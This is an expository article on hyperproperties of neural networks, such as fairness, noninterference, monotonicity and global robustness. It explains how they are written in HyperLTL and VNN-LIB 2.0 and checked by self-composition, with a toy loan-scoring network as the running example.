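# Hyperproperties of neural networks: fairness, noninterference and monotonicity

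## What is a hyperproperty, and why can no single run break one?

A hyperproperty is a requirement on how several runs of a system relate to one another. The usual example, from computer security, is that what a program prints must not depend on a password. A single run can't show whether this holds, because checking it means comparing runs with different passwords. Clarkson and Schneider (2008) named these requirements and developed a general theory of them in *Hyperproperties*, with security policies in mind.

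Researchers have since applied the word to neural networks, because many of the properties people want from a network also compare one run with another. Two loan applicants who differ only in sex should get the same decision. Two nearly identical sensor readings should lead a cruise-control system to nearly identical commands. A risk score should not fall when a risk factor rises. Wurm (2026) notes in *Security Properties of Neural Networks as Decision Problems* that regulation already requires this in credit scoring, insurance pricing and parts of clinical decision support. Testing can find a pair of runs that breaks such a rule, but proving that no such pair exists is much harder, because the proof has to cover every pair of inputs.

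### A network and its runs

The simplest networks are feed-forward: numbers enter at one end, pass through a fixed sequence of layers and leave at the other, with no loops. Each layer does two things. It takes weighted sums of the numbers from the layer before, adding a constant (a bias) to each, and then applies a simple nonlinear function to every sum separately. Fukuda, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Branch and Bound for Relational Verification of Neural Networks*, write a layer as

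x⁽ⁱ⁾ = W y⁽ⁱ⁻¹⁾ + B,  y⁽ⁱ⁾ = σ(x⁽ⁱ⁾)

where y⁽ⁱ⁻¹⁾ holds the previous layer's outputs, W the weights and B the biases. The nonlinear function σ is very often the ReLU, or rectified linear unit, ReLU(z) = max(0, z), which leaves positive numbers alone and turns negative ones into zero. Once training has ended, the weights and biases are constants, and the network is simply a function N from n input numbers to m output numbers.

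A toy network with two inputs and two ReLUs is already enough to show most of the difficulties:

f(x, s) = ReLU(x + s − 1) − ReLU(x − 1), with x in [0, 2] and s in [0, 1].

In this example, a lender uses f to assess loan applicants. The number x summarizes the applicant's finances, and s encodes an attribute that should make no difference, with 0 for one group and 1 for the other. Values of s between 0 and 1 have no meaning for real applicants, but verification tools commonly work on whole intervals. The lender approves the loan when f is at least 0.5, the cut-off that *CertiFair* (Khedr and Shoukry, 2022) uses for its classifiers.

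A run, or trace, is one execution of the network. Athavale, Bartocci and colleagues (2024), in *Verifying Global Two-Safety Properties in Neural Networks with Confidence*, define a trace as the list of values that go into and come out of each layer, in order, starting with the input. On the input (1, 0), both hidden neurons of f compute the sum 0, the ReLUs leave both sums at 0, and the output is 0. On (1, 1), the sums are 1 and 0, and the output is 1.

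In a deterministic network, the input determines everything else in that list, so each input has exactly one run. Each run begins with its input, so different inputs have different runs. Checking a claim for all pairs of runs is therefore the same as checking it for all pairs of inputs. This fails when chance is involved, as in a text generator that samples its next word, because one input then has many runs. Counting the random draws as part of the input restores the equivalence.

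### What one run can refute

Most work on neural network verification concerns requirements that a single run can break. Boetius and Leue (2023), in *Verifying Global Neural Network Specifications using Hyperproperties*, write such a requirement as a pair of sets, an input set X and an output set Y. The network satisfies it if

for all u in X: N(u) is in Y.

Any u in X whose output falls outside Y is a counterexample, and one run is all it takes to exhibit it.

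The claim that the score f always lies between 0 and 1 has the whole domain as X and [0, 1] as Y. This claim is true. Since s is never negative, x + s − 1 is at least x − 1, and adding s inside a ReLU raises the result by at least 0 and at most s, so f always lies between 0 and s. A verifier is a program that looks for proofs like this one in networks too large to check by hand, where testing cannot cover the infinitely many inputs. It is sound if it never certifies a false claim, and complete if it always settles the question given enough time.

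Most verification effort has gone into local robustness. This property fixes one image whose label is known, say a stop sign, and requires the network to classify every image within some small distance of it as a stop sign too. Because the original image never changes, we can write its label into the output set Y, and a single run on one altered image is then enough to refute the claim.

Global robustness lets both images vary over the whole input space and requires any two close images to get similar outputs. As Boetius and Leue point out, we can no longer tell from the output for one arbitrary image whether something has gone wrong, because there is no known label to compare it with. A counterexample must therefore be a pair of images.

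### Sets of runs, and sets of sets of runs

The same problem arises with the toy lender. Two applicants have identical finances, x = 1, but the one with s = 0 gets f = 0 and is refused, while the one with s = 1 gets f = 1 and receives a loan. Either decision at x = 1 is a possible policy, so we can object only when we compare the two runs.

No rule that checks runs one at a time can define fairness between the two groups. Suppose a network were fair exactly when all its runs were on some list P of permitted runs. For any run of f, such as the one on (1, 0), we can build a second network by copying f, setting every first-layer weight to zero, and setting each first-layer bias to the sum that its neuron had in that run. This second network gives the same output for every input, so it is fair, and all its runs must be on the list. Its run on (1, 0) is identical to f's run on (1, 0), so that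 run of f is on the list too. The same construction works for every other run of f, so f would count as fair although it is unfair.

The only fact about fairness that argument uses is that a constant network is fair. A constant network's output also never depends on a secret, never falls when an input rises and never changes much between neighbouring inputs, so none of these requirements reduces to a rule about single runs either.

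The definitions of Clarkson and Schneider make the distinction exact. A system is the set T of all its runs. An ordinary property P is a set of runs as well, the permitted ones, and the system satisfies it if every run of T is in P:

T ⊆ P.

A hyperproperty H is a set of sets of runs, in effect a list of permitted *systems*, and the system satisfies it if the whole set T is one of the entries:

T ∈ H.

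Because a hyperproperty is a set of sets of runs, whether a run is acceptable can depend on which other runs the system has. Clarkson and Schneider (2009) also show, in the longer version of *Hyperproperties*, that any ordinary property P can be rewritten as a hyperproperty H, the set of all subsets of P. Strictly speaking, then, a single run can break some hyperproperties. In practice, people mostly reserve the word for requirements that can only be checked by comparing runs.

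### How many runs does a violation take?

Some comparisons need two runs, others need more, and a few need infinitely many. The classification starts from safety, which means that a certain bad thing never happens. For a single run, the bad thing must appear in finite time and be impossible to undo, as when a program reads a confidential file and then writes to the network. Clarkson and Schneider extend this by letting the bad thing be a finite set of runs instead of one. If that set never has to contain more than k runs, the requirement is k-safety.

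A requirement on networks is k-safety if every network that violates it has at most k runs such that any network with those same runs also violates it. Ordinary safety is the case k = 1. When k = 2, a violation can be shown by a counterexample pair, two inputs whose outputs together break the requirement. The inputs (1, 0) and (1, 1) are such a pair for the toy lender. Any network that gives 0 on one of them and 1 on the other is unfair, whatever it does on other inputs.

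Some hyperproperties have a higher k. In Clarkson and Schneider's example, a system splits a secret into k shares, any k − 1 of which are useless, and must never reveal all k across its runs. If each run reveals one share, proving a leak takes at least k runs. For a neural network and a protected attribute with A possible values, Boetius and Leue compare A copies of each person, one per value, and require that some class score highest for all of them. Two runs are enough to break this requirement, even though it compares A of them, because if the copies do not all land in the same class, at least two of them differ.

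The only complication is ties. If three copies have top-scoring classes {1, 2}, {2, 3} and {1, 3}, every pair shares a class, but no class is common to all three. Wurm avoids this by giving every tie to the class with the smallest index, so each input has exactly one class and the requirement is 2-safety again.

By a theorem in the 2009 paper, if a system satisfies a safety hyperproperty, so does any system with only some of the same runs. For a network, this means that a 2-safety property proved on a large input domain also holds on every smaller domain within it. Requirements outside the safety class may not carry over in this way. Clarkson and Schneider describe a system that picks at random whether to output 0, 1, or the value of a secret bit. The set of values it may output does not depend on the secret. But if only the runs that take the third option remain, the system always outputs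 the secret.

### Four requirements, one formula each

Below, u and u′ are any two inputs from a domain D, N(u) is the network's output for u, and h(u) is the resulting decision, such as approve or refuse.

**Attribute-flip fairness.** Split each input into a protected attribute uₛ and the rest, uᵣ. Then:

for all u, u′ in D: if uᵣ = u′ᵣ and uₛ ≠ u′ₛ, then h(u) = h(u′).

This property has several names. Khedr and Shoukry call a network that satisfies it "nondiscriminatory between individuals", and Boetius and Leue call the property dependency fairness. Wurm calls it counterfactual fairness and replaces the second input with a function that swaps the attribute's value.

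**Noninterference.** Split each input into a public part, u_P, and a secret part. Then:

for all u, u′ in D: if u_P = u′_P, then N(u) = N(u′).

Noninterference comes from the study of secure operating systems and is much older than its use on neural networks. Its formula is almost the same as the fairness formula, with the secret in place of the protected attribute, but it compares exact outputs rather than decisions. For example, the toy inputs (1, 0.6) and (1, 1) have outputs 0.6 and 1. The lender approves both, so the pair satisfies the fairness formula. But if s is a secret, the pair violates noninterference, because the difference between the two scores reveals some information about s.

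**Monotonicity** in input number i:

for all u, u′ in D: if u′ᵢ ≥ uᵢ and u′ⱼ = uⱼ for every other j, then N(u) ≤ N(u′).

The clause about every other j matters because the condition is far stricter without it. Boetius and Leue omit it from their version, in which an output must never rise. Their formula compares any two inputs where one has an i-th coordinate at least as large as the other's, whatever the remaining coordinates are. Two inputs with the same i-th coordinate then satisfy the condition in both directions, so their outputs must be equal, and the output can depend only on coordinate i. Hardly any useful network would satisfy this. In the toy lender, going from (1, 1) to (2, 0) improves the applicant's finances but lowers the score from 1 to 0, which violates monotonicity if the clause is omitted. With the clause, the pair is irrelevant because s has changed as well.

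**Global robustness**, for a distance ε and a tolerance δ:

for all u, u′ in D: if every coordinate of u is within ε of the same coordinate of u′, then |N(u) − N(u′)| ≤ δ.

Fukuda and colleagues use this version, which limits how far a score may move. Athavale and colleagues also give a stricter one, in which nearby inputs must get the same class. The stricter version fails at the boundary between two classes, because nearby inputs on opposite sides get different classes. Repairs for this need separate discussion.

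Each of the four formulas consists of a condition on the two inputs followed by a condition on the two outputs. None of them includes a correct answer, so they can be stated without labelled data, but a network that refuses every applicant satisfies all four. Boetius and Leue similarly note that withholding the attribute from the network trivially satisfies attribute-flip fairness, but is known not to be enough for fairness in the real world.

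The toy lender fares as follows.

| Requirement on f | Verdict | Evidence |
|---|---|---|
| Attribute-flip fairness, s protected | broken | (1, 0) gives 0, (1, 1) gives 1 |
| Noninterference, s secret | broken | the same pair, or (1, 0.6) and (1, 1) |
| Global robustness, ε = 0.1 and δ = 0.1 | broken | (0.5, 0.5) gives 0, (0.6, 0.6) gives 0.2 |
| Monotonicity in x | holds | needs a proof |

The last row differs from the others because no pair of inputs can prove it. Raising x while s is fixed never lowers f, and this claim covers infinitely many pairs. The proof needs a way to handle two runs at once, so it comes later.

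Formulas over inputs are enough for networks whose run is a single pass. For systems that run over time, such as a controller that acts repeatedly, *Temporal Logics for Hyperproperties* (2014) introduced HyperLTL, a logic with the quantifiers "for all runs" and "there is a run".

### Equal approval rates need more than two runs

The kind of fairness that people most often have in mind is about groups. The lender should approve the same share of applicants from each. *Unravelling the (In)compatibility of Statistical-Parity and Equalized-Odds* (2026) collects some of the names for it, among them statistical parity, demographic parity and equal acceptance rate. As *A Comprehensive View of Fairness through Distributional Stability* (2026) puts it in symbols, the approval rate of group g is

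r_g(h) = P(h(X) = 1 | G = g),

the probability of approval for a person X drawn from that group, and the requirement is r₀(h) = r₁(h). Suppose x is spread evenly over [0, 2] in both groups. With s = 0 the toy score is always 0, so the lender approves nobody. With s = 1 it approves everyone whose x is at least 0.5, which is 75% of the group.

This is a hyperproperty, because whether one refusal is acceptable depends on the other decisions. Clarkson and Schneider give a similar example, a limit on a system's mean response time over all its runs, where one slow response may be fine if enough of the others are quick. But equal approval rates are not a 2-safety property. An approved applicant from one group and a refused applicant from the other don't show that the rates differ, because decisions on the remaining applicants can make the rates equal. With 100 people in each group, it takes at least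 101 runs to prove a difference, for instance 51 approvals in one group and 50 refusals in the other. The number grows with the population, and for a continuous population like the one above no finite number of runs is enough.

The theorem about removing runs gives a shorter proof of the same result. Suppose a lender approves one of two applicants from each of two groups, so both approval rates are one half. Removing the refused applicant from one group raises that group's rate to 100% and leaves the other unchanged. Removing runs never breaks a safety hyperproperty, but it breaks this requirement, so the requirement is not k-safety for any k. Clarkson and Schneider place mean response time in liveness, the opposite class from safety, because adding enough quick responses can always bring the average down. Equal approval rates also belong in liveness, because after any finite set of decisions,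 further decisions could still balance the groups.

Whether a pair breaks attribute-flip fairness depends only on the network, but an approval rate also depends on who applies. The toy lender's 75% would be a different number in a town with poorer applicants. In a footnote to their response-time example, Clarkson and Schneider note that a plain average assumes all runs to be equally likely, and that any other case calls for a probability measure on the runs. *HyperPCTL* (2018) introduced a logic for requirements of this probabilistic kind. According to *Fairness as a Program Property* (2016), checking group fairness comes down to computing some probabilities for the program and a model of the population, while checking individual fairness requires reasoning about several runs. The paper also notes that if a program approves 40% of minority applicants and 70% of the majority, there may be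 no short piece of evidence for a person to look at, because the proof can involve infinitely many inputs.

Neither statistical parity nor passing the flip test guarantees the other. Suppose a lender approves applicants from the first group when x is at least 1, and from the second when x is below 1. If half of each group has x of at least 1, both groups have a 50% approval rate, but changing any applicant's group would flip the decision. Cynthia Dwork and colleagues, in *Fairness Through Awareness* (2011), call statistical parity insufficient as a general notion of fairness, and this example shows one reason why. A lender that looks only at x passes the flip test, but it can still refuse most of a group whose values of x are lower.

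## How are requirements on several runs written down?

A controller that acts repeatedly may behave correctly for thirty steps and fail on the next, so requirements on it need formulas about time. Engineers often write these requirements in linear temporal logic (LTL), whose formulas describe how a single run unfolds. HyperLTL extends LTL with names for runs, so one formula can compare several runs step by step.

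### The syntax and meaning of HyperLTL

In HyperLTL, a run is an endless sequence of steps. Each step is a list of the basic facts that hold at that moment, such as "the brake is on". Logicians call these facts atomic propositions. The grammar in *Temporal Logics for Hyperproperties* has two lines:

ψ ::= ∃π. ψ | ∀π. ψ | φ

φ ::= a_π | ¬φ | φ ∨ φ | X φ | φ U φ

The first line puts quantifiers over runs at the front, where ∀π means "for all runs π" and ∃π means "there is a run π". The second line gives the rest of the formula. Its simplest part, a_π, means that fact a holds on run π at the current step. In LTL this is written a, because an LTL formula describes one run at a time. ¬ and ∨ mean "not" and "or", and X φ means that φ holds at the next step. The formula φ₁ U φ₂ ("until") means that φ₂ holds now or at some later step, and that φ₁ holds at every step before then.

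Formulas use three abbreviations. G φ means that φ holds from now on, and F φ means that φ holds eventually. φ₁ W φ₂ ("weak until") is like φ₁ U φ₂, except that φ₂ may never hold, in which case φ₁ must hold forever.

To evaluate a formula, we start from the set T of all runs of the system. Each quantifier assigns a run from T to its variable. Once every variable has a run, the rest reads like LTL with a single clock for all the runs, so X moves them all forward by one step together. For example, the formula

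∀π. ∀π′. G (a_π ↔ a_π′)

requires any two runs to agree on fact a at every step. A system with two runs, one where a is always true and one where it is always false, breaks this formula.

### Noninterference over time

The paper calls public inputs and outputs low-security (L) and secret ones high-security (H). It writes π =_L,out π′ when two runs agree on all public outputs at every step, and π[0] =_L,in π′[0] when they agree on the public inputs at the first step. For a system that receives its inputs at the start, noninterference then becomes

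∀π. ∀π′. π[0] =_L,in π′[0] → π =_L,out π′.

The paper calls this version observational determinism because, to someone who sees only the public part, the system looks like a deterministic function of its public input.

Many systems receive new inputs at every step, and the temporal operators can handle this. Suppose a chat assistant always picks its most probable next word, so that chance plays no part, and its operator has given it a confidential instruction. The public input at each step is the user's message. The requirement that replies reveal nothing about the instruction is

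∀π. ∀π′. (reply_π = reply_π′) W (message_π ≠ message_π′).

Two conversations must have identical replies until the user's messages first differ. After that, the replies may differ too.

A useful assistant would rarely satisfy this, since operators write instructions precisely to change the replies. *Temporal Logics for Hyperproperties* deals with a similar problem in password checkers, which have to reveal whether the password was right. Let pw be the fact that the entered password is correct. The relaxed formula is

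∀π. ∀π′. (π[0] =_L,in π′[0] ∧ X (pw_π ↔ pw_π′)) → π =_L,out π′.

It exempts any pair of runs in which one password was correct and the other was wrong. In every other pair, the two runs must still look the same from outside.

Another option is to limit how much leaks. For a deterministic program whose secret is equally likely to take any of its values, the paper limits the leak to n bits by forbidding any set of 2ⁿ + 1 runs with the same public input and pairwise different public outputs. With n = 1, three such runs violate the limit. If we treat s as the secret, the toy lender's score leaks more than one bit, because at x = 1 the values 0, 0.5 and 1 of s give the scores 0, 0.5 and 1. A lender that publishes only "approved" or "refused" cannot leak more than one bit, because it has only two outputs.

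### Requirements that need "there is a run"

Observational determinism is too strict for systems that make random choices. Two runs with the same public input may then differ for reasons that have nothing to do with the secret. Generalised noninterference allows for this by adding a third run:

∀π. ∀π′. ∃π″. π =_H,in π″ ∧ π′ =_L π″.

For any two runs, there must be a third that has the secret inputs of the first and the public inputs and outputs of the second. Whatever an observer sees during the second run could therefore also have happened with the first run's secret inputs. The system that outputs 0, 1 or a secret bit at random satisfies this, since both outputs are possible whatever the secret is, but it violates observational determinism.

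The formula depends only on which runs are possible, not on how likely they are. If the system picks its three options with equal probability, its output matches the secret two times out of three, so an observer can guess the secret better than by tossing a coin. To rule this out, we need a probabilistic logic, such as HyperPCTL.

No pair of runs can refute generalised noninterference, because the third run it requires might exist but not have been observed yet. The paper therefore classes it as liveness. Formulas that mix "for all" with "there is" are also much harder to check.

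### What remains for a network with a single step

A feed-forward network takes one step, so we can put both its input and output in that step and drop the temporal operators. Observational determinism then reduces to the noninterference formula over inputs.

The third run is also unnecessary when the network is deterministic and its domain contains every combination of a public part and a secret part. It has to start from the input that combines the public part of u′ with the secret part of u, and that input has only one run. Generalised noninterference then requires the output to stay the same when the secret part changes and the public part does not, which is ordinary noninterference.

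Even when time matters, the original HyperLTL cannot express that two real-valued network outputs differ by at most 0.1, because a formula uses finitely many atomic propositions, each of which is true or false of a single run. In practice, people add numerical comparisons between runs to the logic.

### Learned policies that act over time

Time matters when a network has memory or when its actions affect its later inputs. A recurrent network feeds part of its state back into itself, so it can respond differently to the same input at steps 5 and 50. A policy, the rule by which a learned agent picks its actions, receives inputs that depend on its earlier actions.

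Hsu, Rafieioskouei and Bonakdarpour (2025), in *HypRL*, used HyperLTL to specify what a pair of agents should learn. In their opening example, a firefighter and a medic move through a grid of nine cells, three of which are on fire. The firefighter must put out all the fires and the medic must reach two victims, one of them in a burning cell. The two must always stay within two cells of each other, and the medic may not enter a burning cell before the firefighter has been there. The formula begins ∀τ₁. ∃τ₂, where τ₁ is the firefighter's path and τ₂ the medic's. The last condition, for a burning cell f, is

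¬f_τ₂ U f_τ₁,

which means that the medic is not in f until the firefighter is. Hsu and colleagues argue that formulas with only "for all" quantifiers are too restrictive here, because the medic's best path depends on what the firefighter does.

The method has three steps. First, it replaces "there is a path τ₂" with a function that takes the firefighter's path and returns a path for the medic, a standard technique in logic called Skolemization. Second, it turns the remaining formula into a number that measures how well a set of finite paths satisfies it. The number for "A and B" is the smaller of the numbers for A and B, the number for "A or B" is the larger, and the number for "always A" is the smallest value for A over all steps. Third, an ordinary reinforcement-learning algorithm uses this number as its reward and learns the policy and the function together.

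They tested this on four grid maps, in which two agents had to reach their goals without being in the same place at the same time. They compared three versions of CQ-learning, a multi-agent learning algorithm: alone, with a shield (a separate safeguard that blocks unsafe actions), and with HypRL's reward. The table gives the average number of steps to the goal, followed by the average number of collisions.

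| Map | CQ-learning alone | With a shield | With HypRL |
|---|---|---|---|
| ISR | 28.0 steps, 0.19 | 17.4 steps, 0 | 7.6 steps, 0.25 |
| Pentagon | 36.5 steps, 0.28 | 75.2 steps, 0 | 11.9 steps, 0.53 |
| SUNY | 12.0 steps, 0.01 | 11.5 steps, 0 | 12.5 steps, 0 |
| MIT | 41.3 steps, 0.2 | 33.5 steps, 0 | 23.2 steps, 0 |

HypRL's agents were the fastest on three maps, but on two of those they sometimes collided, although the formula requires them *always* to be in different places. Their collision rates on these two maps were no better than those of CQ-learning alone, with differences within the margins of error. Hsu and colleagues prove that the best policies for the rewritten formula are also the best for the original one. Training may not find those policies, however, so using a formula as a reward makes violations less likely but does not rule them out.

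Existing proofs about policies that act over time cover single runs. *LTL Verification of Memoryful Neural Agents* (2025) gives methods for proving LTL requirements for several recurrent agents in an uncertain environment, provided that piecewise-linear constraints can describe the whole system. One of the methods computes bounds on the possible values step by step. LTL can express that a car never leaves its lane, but not that it treats two passengers alike, because that requirement compares runs. Self-composition might extend these proofs to several runs, since it joins a system to a copy of itself and so turns a HyperLTL formula with only "for all" quantifiers into an LTL formula.

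### Small networks that write the specification

For networks with a single step, most verifiers check whether every input in a box gives an output in a given set. A box gives each coordinate its own range, so it can't express a link between two inputs, such as "u′ is within ε of u". Boetius and Leue express the link with two small auxiliary networks, which we can call In and Sat.

1. Choose a box W of free numbers w.
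2. In turns w into the v inputs to compare, u¹, …, uᵛ. As w ranges over W, In produces every tuple that meets the input condition and no others.
3. The network under test, N, runs on each of these inputs.
4. Sat takes all the inputs and outputs and returns a number that is at least 0 exactly when the output condition holds.

The requirement then becomes

for all w in W: Sat(u¹, …, uᵛ, N(u¹), …, N(uᵛ)) ≥ 0, where (u¹, …, uᵛ) = In(w).

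This question is about one input w and one number, so it has the form that verifiers expect.

People build the auxiliary networks In and Sat by hand, without training, from operations that ReLU layers can compute exactly, such as max(a, b) = ReLU(a − b) + b, min(a, b) = −max(−a, −b) and |a| = max(a, −a). The networks therefore introduce no approximation.

Global robustness shows how the construction works. The free numbers are an input x and a shift τ, whose coordinates all lie between −ε and ε. In returns the pair

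(x, clip(x + τ)),

where clip moves any coordinate that has left the domain back to the nearest edge. For the toy lender, x = (1.95, 0.5) and τ = (0.1, 0) give the second input (2, 0.5). Sat returns δ minus the largest difference between corresponding outputs, which is negative exactly when some output has moved by more than δ.

For fairness, In turns one person into the copies that attribute-flip fairness compares, and Sat checks that they share a winning class, a condition made of "and" and "or". Boetius and Leue turn "and" into a minimum and "or" into a maximum, as HypRL does. In the toy lender, let d(u) = f(u) − 0.5 be the margin above the cut-off. Two applicants get the same decision if both margins are positive or both are negative, so

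Sat = max( min(d(u), d(u′)), min(−d(u), −d(u′)) ).

For (1, 0) and (1, 1), the margins are −0.5 and 0.5, and Sat returns −0.5, which is a violation. For (1, 0.6) and (1, 1), the margins are 0.1 and 0.5, and Sat returns 0.1. An applicant exactly at the cut-off has margin 0 and matches any other applicant, because Sat is never negative for such a pair.

Boetius and Leue also express Lipschitz continuity, the requirement that the output never changes by more than K times the change in the input. Sat must take the inputs as well as the outputs here, since the permitted change in the output depends on how far apart the inputs are. If we measure the change in the input by the largest change in any coordinate, the toy lender satisfies this requirement for K = 2 but not for K = 1. The paper's other examples are monotonicity and a second kind of global robustness, which adds a class for inputs on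 which the network may be unstable.

Boetius and Leue ran no experiments. They suggest α,β-CROWN as a promising verifier because it accepts networks with arbitrary connections between their parts. They also note that their formalism doesn't remove the need for specialised techniques.

### A monotonicity formula that demands too much

The formula in the paper's monotonicity example leaves the other coordinates free, so it wrongly requires the network to ignore every input except the i-th. Both the preprint and the version that Boetius and Leue published in a workshop volume have this flaw. Their fairness example requires all the other coordinates to be equal, so the omission is probably a slip.

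The slip carries over into In, which takes two arbitrary inputs, gives the smaller i-th coordinate to the first and the larger to the second, and leaves everything else alone. The corrected set of pairs is

{ (u, u′) : u′ᵢ ≥ uᵢ, and u′ⱼ = uⱼ for every j ≠ i },

with N(u′) ≤ N(u) as the output condition. A matching In needs one full input z and one extra number t from the range of coordinate i:

In(z, t) = ( z with zᵢ replaced by min(zᵢ, t), z with zᵢ replaced by max(zᵢ, t) ).

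This version is also smaller. It has n + 1 free numbers for a network with n inputs, where the original has 2n.

A quick test on the network N(u) = u₂ − u₁ would have revealed the problem. Its output never rises when only u₁ rises, so it should pass for i = 1. The original formula rejects it, because going from (0, 0) to (0, 1) leaves u₁ unchanged and raises the output from 0 to 1. A verifier would report a pair of inputs like this, and a reader would see that the wrong coordinate had changed.

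Mistakes that let a faulty network pass are more dangerous than mistakes that make a correct one fail. If In returned the same input twice by mistake, every network would pass, and there would be no counterexample to reveal the error. It is therefore worth testing a new specification on one network that should pass and one that should fail.

### Trained networks inside a specification

Some conditions, such as "the image contains a stop sign", have no obvious formula. Xie, Kersting and Neider (2022), in *Neuro-Symbolic Verification of Deep Neural Networks*, use trained networks in place of formulas for such conditions. A requirement in their language, NESAL, consists of a condition on the inputs, a list of network runs y₁ ← h₁(x₁), …, y_ℓ ← h_ℓ(x_ℓ), and a condition on the inputs and outputs together. For example, one network can be a stop-sign detector, and the requirement can be that a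 driving network brakes whenever the detector detects a sign. They built a prototype on Marabou, an existing verifier, and tested it with networks for traffic signs and handwritten digits.

Their approach also helps with global requirements, whose counterexamples are often inputs that would never occur in practice. A network that recognises realistic inputs can exclude them, but the proof then depends on how accurate that trained network is. If the detector misses a faded sign, the driving network can ignore that sign too and still pass. The auxiliary networks of Boetius and Leue avoid this problem because they represent their conditions exactly.

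### Languages that verifiers read

VNN-LIB is the standard format for questions to neural network verifiers, and the field's annual competition uses it. Its first version could refer to only one network with one input and one output. *Neural Network Verification is a Programming Language Challenge* (Cordeiro, Daggitt and colleagues, 2025) reports that people therefore couldn't express hyperproperties in it without special tools. The usual workaround was to merge two copies of the network into one file before verification. *VNN-LIB 2.0* (Roy, Antony and colleagues, 2026) objects that the solver then can't reuse what it derives about one copy when it analyzes the other, and that the file it checks isn't the one people deploy.

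In December 2025, Daggitt (2025), in *Release of Version 2.0 of VNN-LIB standard*, announced a new version with support for several networks. Leaving out the line with the version number, a query about whether the toy lender's score can fall when x rises looks like this:

```
(declare-network f
  (declare-input U float32 [2])
  (declare-output Y float32 [1]))

(declare-network f2
  (equal-to f)
  (declare-input V float32 [2])
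  (declare-output Z float32 [1]))

(assert (and (>= U[0] 0.0) (<= V[0] 2.0)))
(assert (and (>= U[1] 0.0) (<= U[1] 1.0)))
(assert (>= V[0] U[0]))
(assert (== V[1] U[1]))
(assert (< Z[0] Y[0]))
```

The first two assertions set the domain. The third makes x at least as large in the second run, and the fourth, which is missing from the monotonicity example above, keeps s the same. The last assertion states the opposite of the property we want to prove, because the solver looks for values that satisfy all the assertions. Any values it finds for U and V are a counterexample pair, and if it proves that none exist, the lender is monotone in x.

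The line "equal-to f" means that both declarations refer to the same model file. Roy and colleagues name monotonicity and global robustness as uses for it, and expect solvers to become much more efficient by sharing deductions between the two copies. A related keyword, "isomorphic-to", is for two networks with the same structure but different weights, such as a network before and after retraining.

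Each variable also has a numeric type, here float32, the 32-bit numbers that computers commonly use for networks. Version 1.0 had no way to specify this, and solvers often reason about exact real numbers instead. The difference can decide whether two runs agree. Take the network

g(x, s) = ReLU(x + s) − ReLU(s)

for x and s of at least 0. In exact arithmetic, the output is always x, so it reveals nothing about s. In float32, with x = 0.000000001 and s = 1, the sum x + s rounds to 1 and the output is 0, while s = 0 gives the output x. Noninterference holds for the real-valued network and fails for the one that actually runs.

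Queries get long when people write them by hand. Cordeiro and colleagues mention a robustness requirement that takes one line of mathematics and a couple of thousand lines of VNN-LIB 1.0. Vehicle is a higher-level language that avoids this. According to *Vehicle* (2024), users write a specification once, and the tool compiles it for training, for verification and for use in interactive theorem provers, programs that check proofs written by people. In Vehicle, lender monotonicity looks roughly like this:

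```
@network
f : Tensor Rat [2] -> Tensor Rat [1]

@property
monotone : Bool
monotone = forall u v .
  valid u and valid v and u ! 0 <= v ! 0 and u ! 1 == v ! 1
    => f u ! 0 <= f v ! 0
```

Here u ! 0 is the first coordinate of u, and "valid" is a separate definition of the domain. Users state what should hold for all pairs and don't have to negate anything.

The language in *Vehicle* (2022) could express requirements that apply a network to two inputs, but Marabou's queries had variables for only one application, so nothing could check them. The paper proposed numbering the applications and giving each its own variables. *Compiling High-Level Neural Network Specifications into VNN-LIB Queries* (2024) described a compiler that recognises when two applications are the same, which requires every input to match if the network has several. In early 2025, Cordeiro and colleagues noted that Vehicle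 still worked with far fewer tools than CAISAR, a similar platform that also handles several networks.

VNN-LIB 2.0 can handle any fixed number of runs, with one declaration for each, but its assertions contain no quantifiers. It can still express requirements of the form "for all runs", because a violation is a set of values that a solver can look for. A violation of generalised noninterference is a pair of runs for which no suitable third run exists. Stating that requires a "for all" inside the query, which VNN-LIB 2.0 does not support.

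## How does joining a network to its own copy reduce two runs to one?

A single run of a larger system can contain two runs of a smaller one. Take a program, write a second copy of it below the first with every variable renamed, and execute the whole text from top to bottom:

```
if s  > 0 then y  := x  + 1 else y  := x
if s2 > 0 then y2 := x2 + 1 else y2 := x2
```

With s secret and x public, noninterference for the one-line program compares two runs. For the two-line program, it is a condition on each single run: if x = x2 at the start, then y = y2 at the end. The run that starts with x = x2 = 3, s = 1 and s2 = 0 ends with y = 4 and y2 = 3, so the one-line program leaks information about s. *Secure Information Flow by Self-Composition* (Barthe, D'Argenio and Rezk, 2004) applied this idea to noninterference and gave it its current name, self-composition.

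For programs in general, running the copies one after the other can miss leaks. If the first copy loops forever, the second never starts and the final check never happens, so the method can accept a program that halts or hangs depending on the secret. Feed-forward networks don't have this problem because they always finish after a fixed number of operations.

### Building the product network

For a neural network, the joined system is called the product network. Athavale and colleagues build theirs from constraints, using one variable for each neuron's weighted sum and another for its value after the ReLU. The construction has four steps.

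1. Copy every variable and every constraint, and mark the copies with a prime. The weights and biases stay the same.
2. Tie the inputs. For noninterference, add the equation xᵢ = x′ᵢ for each public input i, and leave the secret inputs free.
3. Add the opposite of the requirement on the outputs, for instance y ≠ y′.
4. Ask an ordinary verifier whether any values satisfy all the constraints together.

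If no such values exist, the requirement holds for every pair of inputs. If the verifier finds some, we can split them between the two copies to get a counterexample pair, and confirm it by running the original network on both inputs. A run of the product network is a pair of runs of the original, so a verifier that is sound and complete for single runs of the product is also sound and complete for pairs of runs of the original.

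In the toy lender, f(x, s) = ReLU(x + s − 1) − ReLU(x − 1), let x be public and s secret. The product network has four hidden neurons. Once we tie x′ to x, two of them compute ReLU(x − 1) from the same number, and they cancel in the difference of the outputs:

f(x, s) − f(x, s′) = ReLU(x + s − 1) − ReLU(x + s′ − 1).

Since s and s′ lie between 0 and 1, the two sums differ by at most 1, and a ReLU never enlarges a difference, so the expression is at most 1. It reaches 1 at x = 1, s = 1 and s′ = 0, where it equals ReLU(1) − ReLU(0). Splitting this joint input between the two copies gives (1, 1) and (1, 0), the same pair that showed the lender to be unfair.

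We only need to check whether the difference can be positive, because if it were negative for some s and s′, exchanging the two would make it positive. This works whenever exchanging the copies leaves the condition on the inputs unchanged, as it does for noninterference, attribute-flip fairness and global robustness. In monotonicity the two inputs have different roles, but one query is still enough because only one direction counts as a violation.

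More generally, a neuron that doesn't depend on the secret, either directly or through earlier layers, has the same value in both copies, so the product network needs to include it only once. In most trained networks, every first-layer neuron depends on every input, so nothing cancels exactly. The values in the two copies may still be close, and difference bounds make use of this.

Boetius and Leue use the same copies, but their auxiliary networks In and Sat carry out steps 2 and 3. They report that in 2017 verifiers could not yet check global robustness, although self-composition had already made it possible to express the question.

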